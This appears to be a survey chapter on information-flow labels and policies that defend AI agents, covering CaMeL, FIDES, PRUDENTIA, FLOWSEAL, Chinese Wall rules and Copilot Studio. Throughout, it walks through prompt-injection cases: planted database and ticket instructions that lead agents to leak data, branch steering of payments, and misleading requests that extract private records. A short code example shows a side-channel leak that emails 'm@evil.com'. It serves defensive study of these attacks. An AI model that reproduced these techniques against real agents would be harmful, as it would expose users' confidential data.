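Like integrity labels, the tags don't show whether data is true, so CaMeL can email the finance director a summary of false survey figures without breaking a rule. Tallam and Miller point out that a summary could also repeat a planted instruction for the reader to forward a file to an outside address. The agent would have done nothing unauthorized, but the reader might follow the instruction.

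False data can also cause a legitimate plan to take a harmful branch. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* calls this branch steering. Suppose a plan pays an invoice if the supplier's page shows it as overdue. An attacker who alters the page can trigger the payment without adding a step to the plan. A policy could require a person to approve each payment, but that person would need to check the invoice against a source other than the supplier's page.

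Restricting where a value comes from doesn't help if the attacker controls that source. AuthGraph requires flight codes to come from the flight search, so it would accept a fraudulent code if someone had tampered with the search service. Wang and colleagues acknowledge this and leave it out of scope.

### Leaks through a program's behaviour

An agent can reveal a secret without putting it in a message, through indirect routes called side channels. Tallam and Miller give the example of a program that reads a secret number and requests a harmless web page that many times. The requests contain nothing private, but the site's owner can learn the number by counting them. Whether a program fails and how long it takes can also reveal information.

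Garby and colleagues found a subtler leak in how CaMeL tracks data. Suppose a program may not tell an outsider whether an account's balance is above a threshold. CaMeL blocks the obvious version, which sends an email if the balance is high, because the email depends on the balance. But it misses a roundabout version, which works like this:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
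if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the instruction that would change `rich`. The interpreter updates a variable's tags only when the program changes that variable, so `rich` is still tagged as public and the email goes out. If the balance is low, the program sends nothing. The outsider can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives.

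CaMeL has another leak in the code around its interpreter. When a run fails, CaMeL tries again, and its tracking doesn't cover this retry loop. If a policy blocks a run only when a certain digit of a secret is 1, the failure reveals that digit. Repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret.

An attacker can't easily exploit either leak through a web page, because the planner writes the program without seeing the page. The user would have to paste in a malicious request, or the planner would have to accidentally write a program that contains one of the leaks. Still, the leaks mean that CaMeL's tracking doesn't give a complete guarantee.

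Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language that labels every value, including the model's conversation, and gave a computer-checked proof of its protection. The proof does not rule out a program revealing a little information by failing to finish. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, their agent completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. Zhou and colleagues also applied the same rules to the retry code as to the agent's programs.

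### When one agent instructs another

CaMeL protects one agent, but many products have a central agent that gives jobs to specialised ones. Peters-Gill and colleagues built such a system from three CaMeL agents running GPT-5.2. They planted an instruction in the job applicant database to email the data to an outside address, then asked the system to send Julie a summary of the applicants on Slack.

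The database agent and the central agent both safely treated the planted text as data. But the central agent then wrote to the notification agent, in effect, "Send this summary to Julie", followed by the summary. The notification agent treated the entire message as its user's request, so its planner read the planted instruction and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to the outsider.

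The team had switched off CaMeL's policies for this test. A rule against all outside email would have stopped the leak, but a rule based on who was allowed to read the data might not have, because the summary lost its tags when it became part of a request.

The paper's solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and untrusted data between agents through separate channels and keeps the tags attached to the data. On an extended version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. Running CaMeL on each agent separately already stopped nearly all of these attacks, so the improvement matters most against an attacker who knows how the agents pass messages. Multi-CaMeL reduced the number of tasks completed, though only modestly for the strongest models.

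## FIDES and Microsoft's trust and reader labels

CaMeL's planner writes its program before the agent reads anything, so CaMeL works poorly when the next step depends on what an email says. FIDES, a design from Microsoft, keeps the usual loop in which the model chooses one action, receives the result and chooses the next. Code outside the model tracks labels and checks them before each tool call. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the design and reports tests on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used to test CaMeL.

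### One label for the context

FIDES gives the agent's whole context a label with two parts, an integrity level and a list of permitted readers. The user's request and the developer's instructions normally count as trusted and public. When a tool returns a result, the code updates the context's label using the joining rule.

Whatever the model writes next, including a tool call and its arguments, takes the context's label. Software can't reliably tell which parts of the context shaped a model's output, so FIDES assumes that all of them did. As a result, an email recipient chosen by the model can be labeled untrusted even if the model ignored the untrusted email in its context when choosing it.

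Tools can label each field of a result separately, so an email's authenticated sender address can be labeled trusted and its body untrusted. Costa and colleagues also describe a more detailed integrity label that lists everyone who could have written the data. When an agent combines two documents, the list of readers shrinks, but the list of writers grows, because anyone who could have written either document could have influenced the result.

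### Two policies

FIDES has two basic policies. The first allows a consequential action, such as a payment or a deletion, only if the tool call and its arguments are trusted. The second allows a tool call to send data only if everyone who can read the destination is permitted to read the data.

Once the payroll agent has read the survey page, the first policy blocks every email it tries to send, even the one to the finance director, which the second policy would allow. The second policy alone doesn't prevent planted text from steering the agent, but it limits where the steered agent can send the data.

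A company can require a message to satisfy both policies or either one. The either-policy rule permits robust declassification, in which an agent may release data to new readers as long as its context is trusted. Costa and colleagues reason that planted text can't have caused such a release, so they assume it was intentional. They use the either-policy rule for email in their tests.

### Hiding, querying and revealing data

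FIDES hides data in variables, as the dual-LLM pattern does, but only if the data has a stricter label than the context. When part of a tool result does, the code stores that part in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model still sees the rest of the result, and the context's label stays the same, so one stranger's email doesn't restrict everything that follows.

The model can then use the hidden data in three ways:

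- It can pass the variable to another tool. To forward three emails to a colleague on Slack, the model doesn't need to read them.
- It can put a question about the variable to an isolated model that has no tools. The answer goes into a new variable, which inherits the labels of everything the isolated model received.
- It can reveal the variable. The text enters the context, and the context takes on the text's label.

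The design also allows a compromise between the last two. The isolated model's answer can be limited to a fixed set, such as yes or no, as in Willison's pattern, and FIDES can record this limit in the label. A policy may then allow a yes or no from an untrusted source, because the answer carries only one bit of information.

Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one. The agent asks the isolated model whether any email contains a request, and reads only the yes-or-no answer. If the answer is yes, the agent has the isolated model extract the details into a variable and passes that variable to the calendar.

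A stranger's email can therefore influence the plan by only one bit, but anyone who sends a plausible request can still choose the event's time and participants unless the policy also checks where those arguments came from. Ten yes-or-no answers can together distinguish 1,024 possibilities, so a policy that accepts such answers should limit how many questions the agent may ask.

### Which tasks need the data

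Costa and colleagues sort tasks by how much the agent has to know about the data. They classified AgentDojo's tasks by hand:

| Kind of task | Example | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| The steps are fixed, and no model has to read the data | Forward three emails | 47.5% | 0% | 18.7% | 19.0% |
| The steps are fixed, but a model has to process the text | Summarize three emails and send the summary | 47.5% | 90.0% | 37.5% | 38.1% |
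| The steps depend on the data | Create an event if an email asks for a meeting | 5.0% | 10.0% | 43.8% | 42.9% |

FIDES can in principle do the first two kinds of task without revealing anything, but for the third it must reveal at least a yes or no. Many of the banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the trusted-action policy forbids when the file is untrusted.

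### Results on AgentDojo

When GPT-4o ran without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES, which could still reveal planted text and obey it. With the checks on, no attacks succeeded against either agent.

The checks cost far more completed tasks in the ordinary agent than in FIDES. These are the completion rates with OpenAI's o1, a stronger model at reasoning, when nobody was attacking:

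| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 70.0% | 82.0% | 96.2% | 87.6% | 84% |
| Ordinary, with checks | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% | 44% |
| FIDES, with checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% | 61% |

Hiding data recovers about two-fifths of the task performance lost to the checks. Part of the remaining loss is deliberate, because some tasks require the agent to obey untrusted text, which the checks are meant to prevent.

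The absence of successful attacks is less impressive than it sounds, because Costa and colleagues labelled a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack targeted it. The labels were therefore right about every attack in the test, whereas a company has to guess where attacks will come from. They also discounted some attacks that AgentDojo had scored as successful, either because the policies had blocked the call or because the policies permitted it. One permitted attack created a calendar event with no participants, and another got the agent to recommend a place to the user.

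The policies in the tests were also looser than the basic trusted-action policy. For payments, they required a trusted decision to pay but did not check the labels on the arguments. If the user asks the agent to pay a bill, the agent can have the isolated model extract the account number from the bill and pay without breaking a rule. An attacker who had changed the account number on the bill would receive the money. Checking the account number's label would prevent this. The same gap lets an attacker replace Bob's address in the dual-LLM pattern.

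Hiding data can also cause ordinary mistakes by leading the model to guess. In one banking task, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. FIDES showed the model the amounts and dates but hid the descriptions. The model decided that a large payment was suspicious and changed the password without reading what the payment was for. The policy allowed the change because the model's context was still trusted. A simpler version of FIDES, with no way to query or reveal variables, picked a highly rated hotel without seeing any ratings. Both guesses happened to be right, and AgentDojo counted the tasks as complete, but a user would not want an agent to guess about a password.

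### Planning around the policies

Completion rates treat a blocked tool call as a failure. In practice, the agent would usually ask a person for approval, as many agents without labels already do before every consequential action. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) therefore counts how many approvals each design needs.

The PRUDENTIA agent adds three things to FIDES. It tells the model about the labels and policies so that the model can plan around them. It requires the model to explain its plan before revealing a variable. It also lets the model ask the user to endorse hidden text, which enters the context as trusted if the user agrees.

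Endorsement can save a lot of approvals. If an untrusted email lists ten errands that each require a consequential tool call, the user can endorse the email with one approval instead of approving all ten calls.

The benefit depended heavily on the model. The table shows the total number of requests to a person across all the AgentDojo tasks that each agent completed, and the share of all tasks that it completed without any:

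| Agent | Requests, GPT-4o | Completed without a request, GPT-4o | Requests, GPT-5 | Completed without a request, GPT-5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, asks before every consequential action | 59.4 | 28.0% | 52.0 | 35.1% |
| Ordinary with labels | 39.4 | 38.4% | 40.4 | 43.4% |
| FIDES | 7.8 | 50.3% | 41.3 | 57.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 23.8 | 42.5% | 7.3 | 72.7% |

With GPT-4o, PRUDENTIA asked about three times as often as FIDES, though it completed slightly more tasks overall. With GPT-5, it asked less than a fifth as often as FIDES. With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA's planning raised its input token use to three to six times that of FIDES.

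An endorsement and an approval each count as one request, but an endorsement permits more. If the email with the ten errands also contains a planted eleventh, a user who endorses the email after reading only the first few lines has approved the planted errand too. Kolluri and colleagues assume that a person would stop any harmful call caused by planted text. That assumption is optimistic for individual approvals, and more so for endorsing a long email.

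PRUDENTIA has no equivalent shortcut for declassification. Kolluri and colleagues left it out because whether data should be released depends on the situation, so they prefer to ask about each tool call. Endorsement arguably depends on the situation too, since a supplier's email may be reliable for a delivery date but not for a new bank account.

They also acknowledge that labels can replace human approval only as protection against attacks. A call can pass every check even when the model has misunderstood the task, so an agent that asks for fewer approvals gives its user fewer chances to notice a mistake.

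### A reply that only Alex may read

About a year after the GitHub attack, Microsoft described how to build such labels into real products. One of its examples involves no attacker. Alex asks an agent to deal with the unanswered emails in an inbox. One email, from Priya, previews the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't authorized to see them yet. After reading both, the agent could include the figures in its reply to Marco just to be helpful.

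The labels prevent this, because the reply could contain information from both emails:

```
readers(Priya's email) = {Alex, Priya}
readers(Marco's email) = {Alex, Marco}
readers(reply)         = {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

Marco isn't on the reply's list of readers, so the agent can't send it to him without asking. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the reply's readers would be {Alex, Marco}, and the agent could send it to him without asking.

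The rule is also stricter than Alex would like. A reply to Marco that says only "I'll get back to you" gets the label {Alex}, because the agent wrote it after reading Priya's email. A thank-you note to Priya gets the same label because the context now includes Marco's message. An agent that handled each email in a fresh context would avoid both problems, but it couldn't use one email to answer another.

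Alex can still approve these replies. The approval screen can name the people who would gain access, because the labels identify them. Asking Alex whether Marco may see something from Priya's email is more useful than asking a general question about sending an email.

### Labels in MCP and the prototypes

An agent needs labels from every tool it uses, and different companies build those tools. Microsoft puts the labels in a metadata field that MCP already provides in tool calls and results, so software that doesn't understand labels can ignore them. A label can cover a whole message or a single field. Servers can also publish a policy for each tool in Rego, a language for writing access rules, and the agent's software evaluates the policy before calling the tool.

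Microsoft and GitHub added labels to GitHub's MCP server as an optional feature. The server gives each result one label, marking content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private ones as private and trusted. If an agent has read both kinds, its context is private and untrusted, and Microsoft's policy stops it from posting publicly. This blocks the leak that Invariant Labs demonstrated. But as Microsoft describes it, the policy applies only to contexts that are both private and untrusted. An agent that had read only private repositories would have a trusted context, so the policy wouldn't stop it from posting their contents publicly by mistake.

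GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal, has an experimental setting that keeps a context label and enforces policies for selected tools from GitHub's MCP server. When Microsoft described the setting, it did not yet cover that server's other tools or any other MCP server, so a developer who also connected a mail server could not rely on the policies to control what the agent emailed.

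The prototype for Microsoft's Agent Framework, a developer toolkit, is closer to the full FIDES design. It hides untrusted results in variables and lets the agent query them through an isolated model or reveal them. When a call breaks a policy, the software blocks it or asks a person, depending on the developer's settings.

Microsoft released an open-source gateway that adds labels for servers that don't supply them. Someone has to describe each tool's output, write a function that works out the labels, and choose or write a policy, which is a lot of work for a server with dozens of tools. Microsoft suggests a shortcut that uses the hints MCP servers can give about their tools. For example, the software could always allow a tool marked as read-only and limited to a closed system, and require public arguments for a read-only tool that contacts the outside world. A wrong hint would lead to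 a wrong decision, so the company would have to trust whoever wrote the hints.

Microsoft planned to work with the MCP community on a common proposal for labels and policies. Until MCP has one, each pair of products has to agree on what the labels mean.

### The Teams policy, line by line

Microsoft published one complete policy, for a tool that posts messages to a Teams channel. The policy starts by making "deny" the default and defining the three possible decisions: allow, deny and ask. It reads the integrity label of the context and the reader list of the message text, then fetches the channel's members from the Teams server. From these it works out which members may not read the text, and it prepares a warning that lists their IDs. In simplified form, the rest is:

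```
missing = channel members who may not read the text

if the context is trusted           -> allow
else if missing contains 0 people   -> allow
else if missing contains 0 or more  -> ask the user
else                                -> deny
```

The first test implements robust declassification. If the context is trusted, the policy allows the message no matter who is in the channel. Planted text can't exploit this rule as long as the labels are right, but the model can still make a mistake.

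Suppose the payroll clerk types in the survey figures herself and asks the agent to post a summary to the finance director's private channel. The agent reads only the payroll file, which the firm labels as trusted. It then picks a channel with a similar name that has 200 members and posts the whole file. Because the context is trusted, comparing the channel's members with the file's permitted readers doesn't affect whether the post is allowed.

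The policy would also fail to prevent the leak in Microsoft's own email example if a company applied the same order of checks to email and labelled messages from colleagues as trusted. The agent's context would stay trusted after it read Priya's and Marco's emails, so the policy would skip the reader check and the agent could send Marco the figures. Microsoft warns in the same post that a model's mistake can do anything that a user's request can, which is a good reason not to skip that check.

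Checking readers in every context would catch these mistakes:

| Context | Channel members | Microsoft's Teams policy | Policy that always checks readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted | All may read the text | Allow | Allow |
| Trusted | Some may not | Allow | Ask |
| Untrusted | All may read the text | Allow | Allow |
| Untrusted | Some may not | Ask | Ask |

The stricter policy would sometimes ask the user about a release they had explicitly requested, such as sending a report to a new colleague. The software could skip the question when the user had named the exact channel or recipient, and ask when the model had chosen it. FIDES can enforce the stricter policy without design changes. In their AgentDojo tests, Costa and colleagues required both a trusted context and permitted readers before the agent could add people to a calendar event.

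Both policies allow a message from an untrusted context if everyone in the channel may read it. An attacker could therefore plant text that gets the agent to post a false announcement, even though nothing would leak.

The final "deny" is probably unreachable. The number of missing people can't be negative, so the third test succeeds whenever the second fails. The policy could reach the last line only if it failed to count them, which is unlikely because Rego normally treats a set built from missing data as empty.

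That behaviour could cause a worse problem if the request for the channel's members failed and returned nothing. The set of recipients would be empty, so no recipient would be missing from the permitted readers and the policy would allow the message. Microsoft doesn't explain how the software handles a failed request, and the software may stop with an error instead. A safer policy would confirm that the member list had arrived before using it.

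If the policy works as intended, it never blocks a message outright, so a user can approve any release. A company that wanted to ban some releases would need another rule. The warning also lists user IDs, which few people would recognise, so the approval screen would have to show names instead.

### Labels that spread or start out wrong

Labels can severely restrict an agent as they spread. With o1, the ordinary agent with checks completed only 17.1% of the Slack tasks. Variables help, but only if the model uses them well. In one Slack task, the model fetched a list of channels that it didn't need and made its own context untrusted. Costa and colleagues hid data in variables only when its integrity label was stricter than the context's, so their tests don't show how well variables would prevent reader lists from shrinking.

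Labels spread because a model mixes all its inputs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper, lists separating the information again as an open research challenge. Costa and colleagues cite a partial solution that identifies which messages influenced an answer and regenerates the answer from those messages alone. If the agent's reply to Marco didn't depend on Priya's email, the software could regenerate the reply without it, and the new reply's label would allow Marco to read it. This requires extra model calls, and the selection may leave out something the agent needed.

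Labels can also be wrong from the start. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts the labels, and the code that carries and enforces them, among the parts of a system that must work correctly for any guarantee to hold. If the payroll file is marked as public, even correct code will let the agent send it to anyone.

Many labels are educated guesses. Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, but someone may have shared it with more people. This error leads to unnecessary questions, which is fairly harmless. GitHub's labels can be wrong in a dangerous way, because they mark outsiders' text in a private repository as trusted.

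Costa and colleagues mention that a system might change a document's label from untrusted to trusted after a prompt injection detector has passed it, but they warn against relying too much on such detectors. The success of Nasr and colleagues' adaptive attacks suggests that the warning should be stronger. If an attacker got a malicious document past the detector, the system would then label it trusted.

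### What an agent's choices reveal

FIDES's confidentiality guarantee covers the data in a tool call but not what an observer can infer from the agent's decision to make the call. Computer scientists call this limited guarantee explicit secrecy.

Suppose an agent reads a confidential decision on whether to close an office. If the office is closing, the agent emails the staff a public article about finding a new job, which it had stored in a variable earlier. Anyone may read the article, so the message passes the reader check, but the staff can easily guess from receiving it that the office is closing.

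Costa and colleagues chose this limit deliberately. A guarantee that covered such inferences would essentially forbid an agent from doing anything publicly visible after reading anything secret. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, which tracks private data on Android phones, make the same compromise. An agent would usually need many visible actions to reveal a long document this way, but only one to send it.

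Garby and colleagues accept that the compromise and the rule that lets yes-or-no answers from untrusted data pass are both defensible, but object that they make the system hard to audit. A reviewer can't tell from the record of a run whether a value that passed was an intended exception or a leak. Costa and colleagues left the yes-or-no rule out of their tests, so there is no evidence of how it would perform.

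In Garby and colleagues' LLMbda language, an exception must be an explicit instruction in the program, so a reviewer can find every place where the program endorses data. They also prove that endorsing data leaves the confidentiality guarantee intact. If the payroll agent endorses the survey's figures, for example, the payroll file stays as secret as before. The proof covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during a run, whereas FIDES's guarantee applies to one particular agent loop.

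However, neither guarantee helps if the payroll file starts with the wrong label. A reviewer who finds an endorsement in LLMbda may also be unable to tell whether it was wise.

### When the recipient is the attacker

Someone can also get private data from an agent with a misleading request, without planting an instruction to override the user's. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) studies agents that hold one person's data and handle requests from others. In its main example, Jane's agent knows Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his ex-wife Emily wants it.

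Earlier defences had instructed the model to recognise requests for private information and obtain consent. The team devised three attacks that don't look like such requests:

- Emily shares a page for a joint project and invites Jane to fill in her professional notes. The agent treats this as ordinary work and writes down what it knows about Mark.
- Emily shares a list of true and false statements about Mark and asks the agent to delete the errors. The agent writes nothing private, but the remaining statements are the true ones.
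- Emily asks by email for a reply of just "completed", while a shared page tells the agent to enter the details there. The agent doesn't connect the harmless email with the disclosure on the page.

Shim and colleagues' system, FLOWSEAL, uses ordinary code to intercept every attempt to write or share data. The code allows messages to people the data's owner has approved and blocks messages to known bad accounts. For any other recipient, if the agent might be disclosing protected records, a separate model compares the proposed text with those records and returns "safe" or "blocked". This model doesn't receive the conversation, so Emily can't influence its decision by telling the agent she is a colleague.

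The team compared FLOWSEAL with an earlier defence that gave the agent detailed instructions for checking identity and consent:

| Attack | Private items leaked with instructions only | Private items leaked with FLOWSEAL |
|---|---|---|
| Shared project page | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Deleting false statements | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Separate email and page | 43.8% | 2.2% |

The checks in code mattered most. When the team removed the interceptor but kept the privacy instructions, the shared-page attack leaked 28.4% of items. But FLOWSEAL also depends on the second model to judge the text. When the team kept the interceptor and replaced the second model with automatic approval, the same attack leaked 24.9%. With automatic refusal, hardly anything leaked, but the agent completed none of its ordinary tasks. The formal guarantee likewise excludes cases where the second model wrongly answers "safe".

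Most of these tests used DeepSeek-V3.2, though two other models gave similar results on the shared-page attack. The team also left prompt injection out of scope, so FLOWSEAL's low leak rates are little evidence of how well it would protect an agent that reads hostile web pages.

Shim and colleagues claim that FIDES would be vulnerable to their attacks because its model does all the policy enforcement. They didn't test this claim, and it contradicts the FIDES paper, in which code outside the model checks the labels and stops tool calls that break the policy. If the software labelled Emily's page as untrusted and Mark's diagnosis as readable only by Mark and Jane, a reader check would stop the agent from writing the diagnosis on the page. The attack could still work under robust declassification if the software labelled Emily's messages as trusted, perhaps because she was a known contact. It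 could also work if nobody had thought to treat deleting a line as a way of sending data.

Agents with FLOWSEAL completed 72.4% of tasks that involved no private data, almost as many as the 75.9% completed by agents with the least strict instructions. But in tests where Mark would agree to share if asked, agents with FLOWSEAL disclosed only 32.7% of the items that Emily legitimately needed, compared with between 61.0% and 85.6% for agents with the other defences. This was mainly because the agents with FLOWSEAL asked Mark for permission less often.

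## Sources that may not be joined: the Chinese Wall policy and Copilot Studio's connector groups

Reader lists like those in FIDES can't enforce the payroll firm's ban on a table of what each sick employee earns, because the head of personnel is allowed to read both source files. The firm needs a separate rule against combining them.

This kind of aggregation adds no new facts, but joined data can also let someone infer a fact that no source contains. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to systems that use MCP, gives the example of a calendar entry for a meeting with "Dr. Smith", location data showing the user in a medical building, and public health records. Together they can reveal that the user is receiving treatment for a specific condition.

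NIST has asked how to determine the sensitivity of data that an agent aggregates, a question that is hard to answer in general. It is simpler to decide in advance which sources conflict and keep them apart. Financial firms applied this approach to their staff long before AI agents existed.

### Two banks and an oil company

A firm may advise companies that compete with each other. An analyst who knows one bank's plans shouldn't advise its rival, and financial firms call the barrier that prevents this a Chinese wall. Brewer and Nash's *The Chinese Wall Security Policy*, a 1989 conference paper, turned this practice into rules that a computer can enforce. In the UK at the time, the Stock Exchange's requirements for these walls had the force of law.

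In their model, all the files about one company form a company dataset, and the datasets of competing companies form a conflict-of-interest class. A person may read at most one dataset in each class but can choose which one. The software records what each person has read and applies two rules:

```
read a file:      allowed if every file read so far is from the same company
                  or from a different conflict-of-interest class
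write to a file:  allowed if the read rule allows access to it, and every file
                  read so far is from the same company or is sanitized
```

Sanitized data is company data that someone has disguised so that readers can't tell which company it describes. Anyone may read it.

Suppose a consulting firm holds data on Bank A, Bank B and an oil company. The banks form one class, and the oil company is in another. The firm applies the rules to an agent that starts with no history:

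| Request | Read so far | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| Read Bank A's loan book | Nothing | Allow |
| Save a note in Bank A's folder | Bank A | Allow |
| Read the oil company's forecast | Bank A | Allow, because it is in a different class |
| Read Bank B's loan book | Bank A, oil company | Block |
| Save a note in the oil company's folder | Bank A, oil company | Block |
| Save another note in Bank A's folder | Bank A, oil company | Block |

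If the agent had started with Bank B, the read rule would have blocked Bank A instead. So, unlike with an ordinary OAuth token, whether a request is allowed depends on what the agent has already accessed.

The last two decisions prevent a leak through a second agent. Suppose the second agent has read Bank B's data, and both agents use the oil company's folder. Neither agent has broken the read rule. But if the first one saves a memo there that mentions Bank A's lending terms, the second can read it and will then have data from both banks. The write rule prevents this whether the first agent includes the terms by mistake or because it is following planted text.

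Sanitized data is meant to let analysts compare rivals, but it is hard to produce when a class is small. An agent that knows Bank A's profit can work out Bank B's exactly from the average of the two. Brewer and Nash acknowledge that sanitization needs enough data to prevent such inferences, but they assume it is possible and pursue the problem no further.

### How many separate readers the policy needs

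Brewer and Nash proved that a firm needs at least as many readers as there are datasets in its largest class if every dataset is to have a reader. The consulting firm needs two, one for each bank, and a firm that advises five car makers needs five. Even five may not be enough, because if they all choose to read the same oil company's data, nobody can read its rival's.

In 1989 each extra reader meant employing another analyst, whereas starting another agent session costs very little. But if one analyst runs both sessions and reads both answers, she learns about both banks. Brewer and Nash anticipated this problem with ordinary programs and insisted that the history belong to the human user, since otherwise anyone could read two rivals' data by using a different program for each.

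Attaching the history only to people also has a drawback. Sandhu (1992), in *A Lattice Interpretation of the Chinese Wall Policy*, points out that under the write rule, someone who has read about two companies can't write anything. An analyst could work normally for one client but couldn't save any work after reading about a second, which Sandhu considers unacceptable.

His solution gives the person and the program separate labels. The analyst's label records every company she has read about, and it can only grow. Each time she logs in, she chooses a label for that session within the limits of her own, and every program she runs in the session keeps that label. With agents, she could run one session for Bank A and another for the oil company, and each could save its work in its client's folder, but she could never start a session for Bank B.

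### Source labels instead of reader lists

Brewer and Nash also claimed that the Bell-LaPadula model, with its fixed levels and permissions, could not correctly represent their policy. With three classes of three companies each, an analyst may have any of 27 combinations of one company per class. An administrator could assign each analyst a combination in advance, but the analysts would then lose their free choice. If an analyst fell ill, the administrator also couldn't tell from the permissions whether a colleague could take over a client, because that depends on what the colleague has read.

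Sandhu disputed the claim, though he conceded that the original Bell-LaPadula model lacked the growing user labels he needed. His labels have one position for each conflict-of-interest class, which contains the name of a company or nothing. Software combines them like this:

```
[Bank A, none] + [none, Oil]    = [Bank A, Oil]
[Bank A, none] + [Bank B, none] = forbidden
```

The label at the top of the lattice is "forbidden", and no person or session may hold it. The joining rule in systems such as FIDES can therefore enforce a rule against combining certain sources, provided that the labels record which sources the data came from as well as who may read it. For the payroll firm, payroll and sickness records would form a class, and any result based on both would get the forbidden label.

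A session labelled [Bank A, Oil] can also save a report that draws on both clients, as long as the report carries the same label. The second agent couldn't read the report, because that agent's label contains Bank B. *On the Chinese Wall Model* (Kessler, 1992) relaxes the write rule differently, by letting the list of conflicts change over time. In the example, the oil company's folder would presumably start to conflict with Bank B once it contained Bank A's data.

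Both designs still need someone to list the conflicts. The classes in Brewer and Nash's model can't overlap, so a conglomerate that competes with both the banks and the oil company doesn't fit properly into either class. The model also covers only conflicts between two datasets at a time. If three datasets are harmless in pairs but sensitive together, the firm has to ban one of the harmless pairs or use a more complicated rule.

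### Copilot Studio's data groups

Copilot Studio is Microsoft's tool for building agents. An agent made with it uses connectors, which link it to data sources, to other services and to the channels where people talk to it. Microsoft's *Configure data loss prevention policies for copilots*, documentation from when the company still called these agents copilots, explains how an administrator can sort the connectors into three groups:

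- **Business** connectors can share data with one another.
- **Non-business** connectors can also share data with one another, but not with business connectors.
- **Blocked** connectors are unavailable.

Suppose an administrator puts SharePoint in the business group and public websites in the non-business group. An employee who builds an agent that draws on both gets an error and can't publish the agent. People who chat with an agent may also see errors if they trigger something the policy forbids.

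The administrator can also filter endpoints, the addresses that a connector may reach. Microsoft lists this option for SharePoint and OneDrive and for public websites, so a company could allow one salary survey site and deny the rest of the web. An administrator can block uploaded documents, a third kind of knowledge source, altogether, but Microsoft lists no endpoint filter for them.

These policies would have stopped the stranger's attack on the payroll agent if public websites and the payroll file had been in different groups, because nobody could have published an agent that used both. They would not have stopped the agent from emailing the file to the recruiter, because the company would have to put email in the same group as the payroll file for the agent to send the finance director a summary.

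The connector groups are much simpler than a Chinese wall, and they separate different things:

| | Chinese Wall policy | Copilot Studio data groups |
|---|---|---|
| What the rule keeps apart | Data about competing companies | Kinds of connector |
| What the decision depends on | What the reader has already read | The groups the administrator has chosen |
| When the conflict comes to light | When someone asks for a rival's data | Usually when someone builds or publishes the agent |
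| Can one agent use either of two conflicting sources? | Yes, but only the first one it reads | Only if its builder removes the other one |

The fixed rule is easier to check because an administrator can tell whether an agent complies before anyone uses it, without keeping a history. But it is too coarse for the consulting firm. If both banks' files are in SharePoint, they share a connector, so they are always in the same group. An endpoint filter could remove Bank B's site, but the consultants who work for Bank B would then need agents under a different policy. With only two usable groups, one policy also couldn't separate three rival clients, even if each had its own connector.

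Administrators can also loosen enforcement by exempting a particular agent, applying the policy only to agents created after a chosen date, or using a "soft" mode that shows errors without blocking the actions that caused them. Enforcement was off by default in this version of Microsoft's documentation, but that may have changed.

### Putting separated data back together

Suppose an agent in Copilot Studio copies the payroll figures into a shared table. If the table's connector is in the business group, an agent that reads public websites can't use it. But within the business group, an agent could combine Bank A's and Bank B's figures in the same table without breaking any rule. Brewer and Nash's write rule would prevent this, as it did with the oil company's folder.

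A person can get around either system by passing the data along themselves. An employee could download the payroll file from SharePoint and upload it to a different agent. Microsoft treats uploaded documents as a separate connector, which may be in the non-business group, and describes no check on where a document came from. With a Chinese wall, an analyst could read Bank A's data and phone a colleague who works for Bank B. Sandhu argues that no computer system can stop a determined consultant from doing this, so the firm has to trust its consultants. He thinks the software should instead guard against Trojan horses, which are programs that misuse their user's access without the user's knowledge. An agent that obeys planted text can misuse its user's access in much the same way.

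Agents can also pass work to each other and so rejoin what an administrator has separated. If a company lets one agent read tickets and another change records, this separation limits the damage each could do only if the first can't ask the second for help.

### ServiceNow's agents recruit one another

In 2025 Aaron Costello, then a researcher at the security company AppOmni, found this weakness in ServiceNow, a platform that companies use to handle IT requests and other internal work. ServiceNow's Now Assist agents can find other agents and pass tasks to them, even if nobody has put them in the same workflow. The agents must be on the same team and marked as discoverable, and the language model must support the feature. All three were true by default. Agents published to the same channel automatically joined one team, often without their owners realising it.

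Costello set up two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents for an administrator. One read and categorized support tickets, and the other could read, create and update records. He also created an ordinary user who could submit tickets but not read other people's. This user submitted a ticket with planted instructions to copy the contents of another ticket into this one, with help from other agents if necessary.

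When the administrator asked for the ticket to be categorized, the first agent recruited the second. The second copied the confidential text into the attacker's ticket, where the attacker could read it. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to give a user the administrator role and to send data out by email.

The recruited agent had different tools, but both agents acted with the administrator's permissions, so each step passed an ordinary permission check, as in the GitHub attack. Checking who could read the source and the destination would have caught the leak, because the attacker could read the destination ticket but not the source.

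According to AppOmni, ServiceNow confirmed that the agents were behaving as intended and updated its documentation. Costello agreed, telling The Hacker News (2025) that this was "expected behavior as defined by certain default configuration options" and not a bug, which he found alarming. The documentation protects only customers who read it and change their settings.

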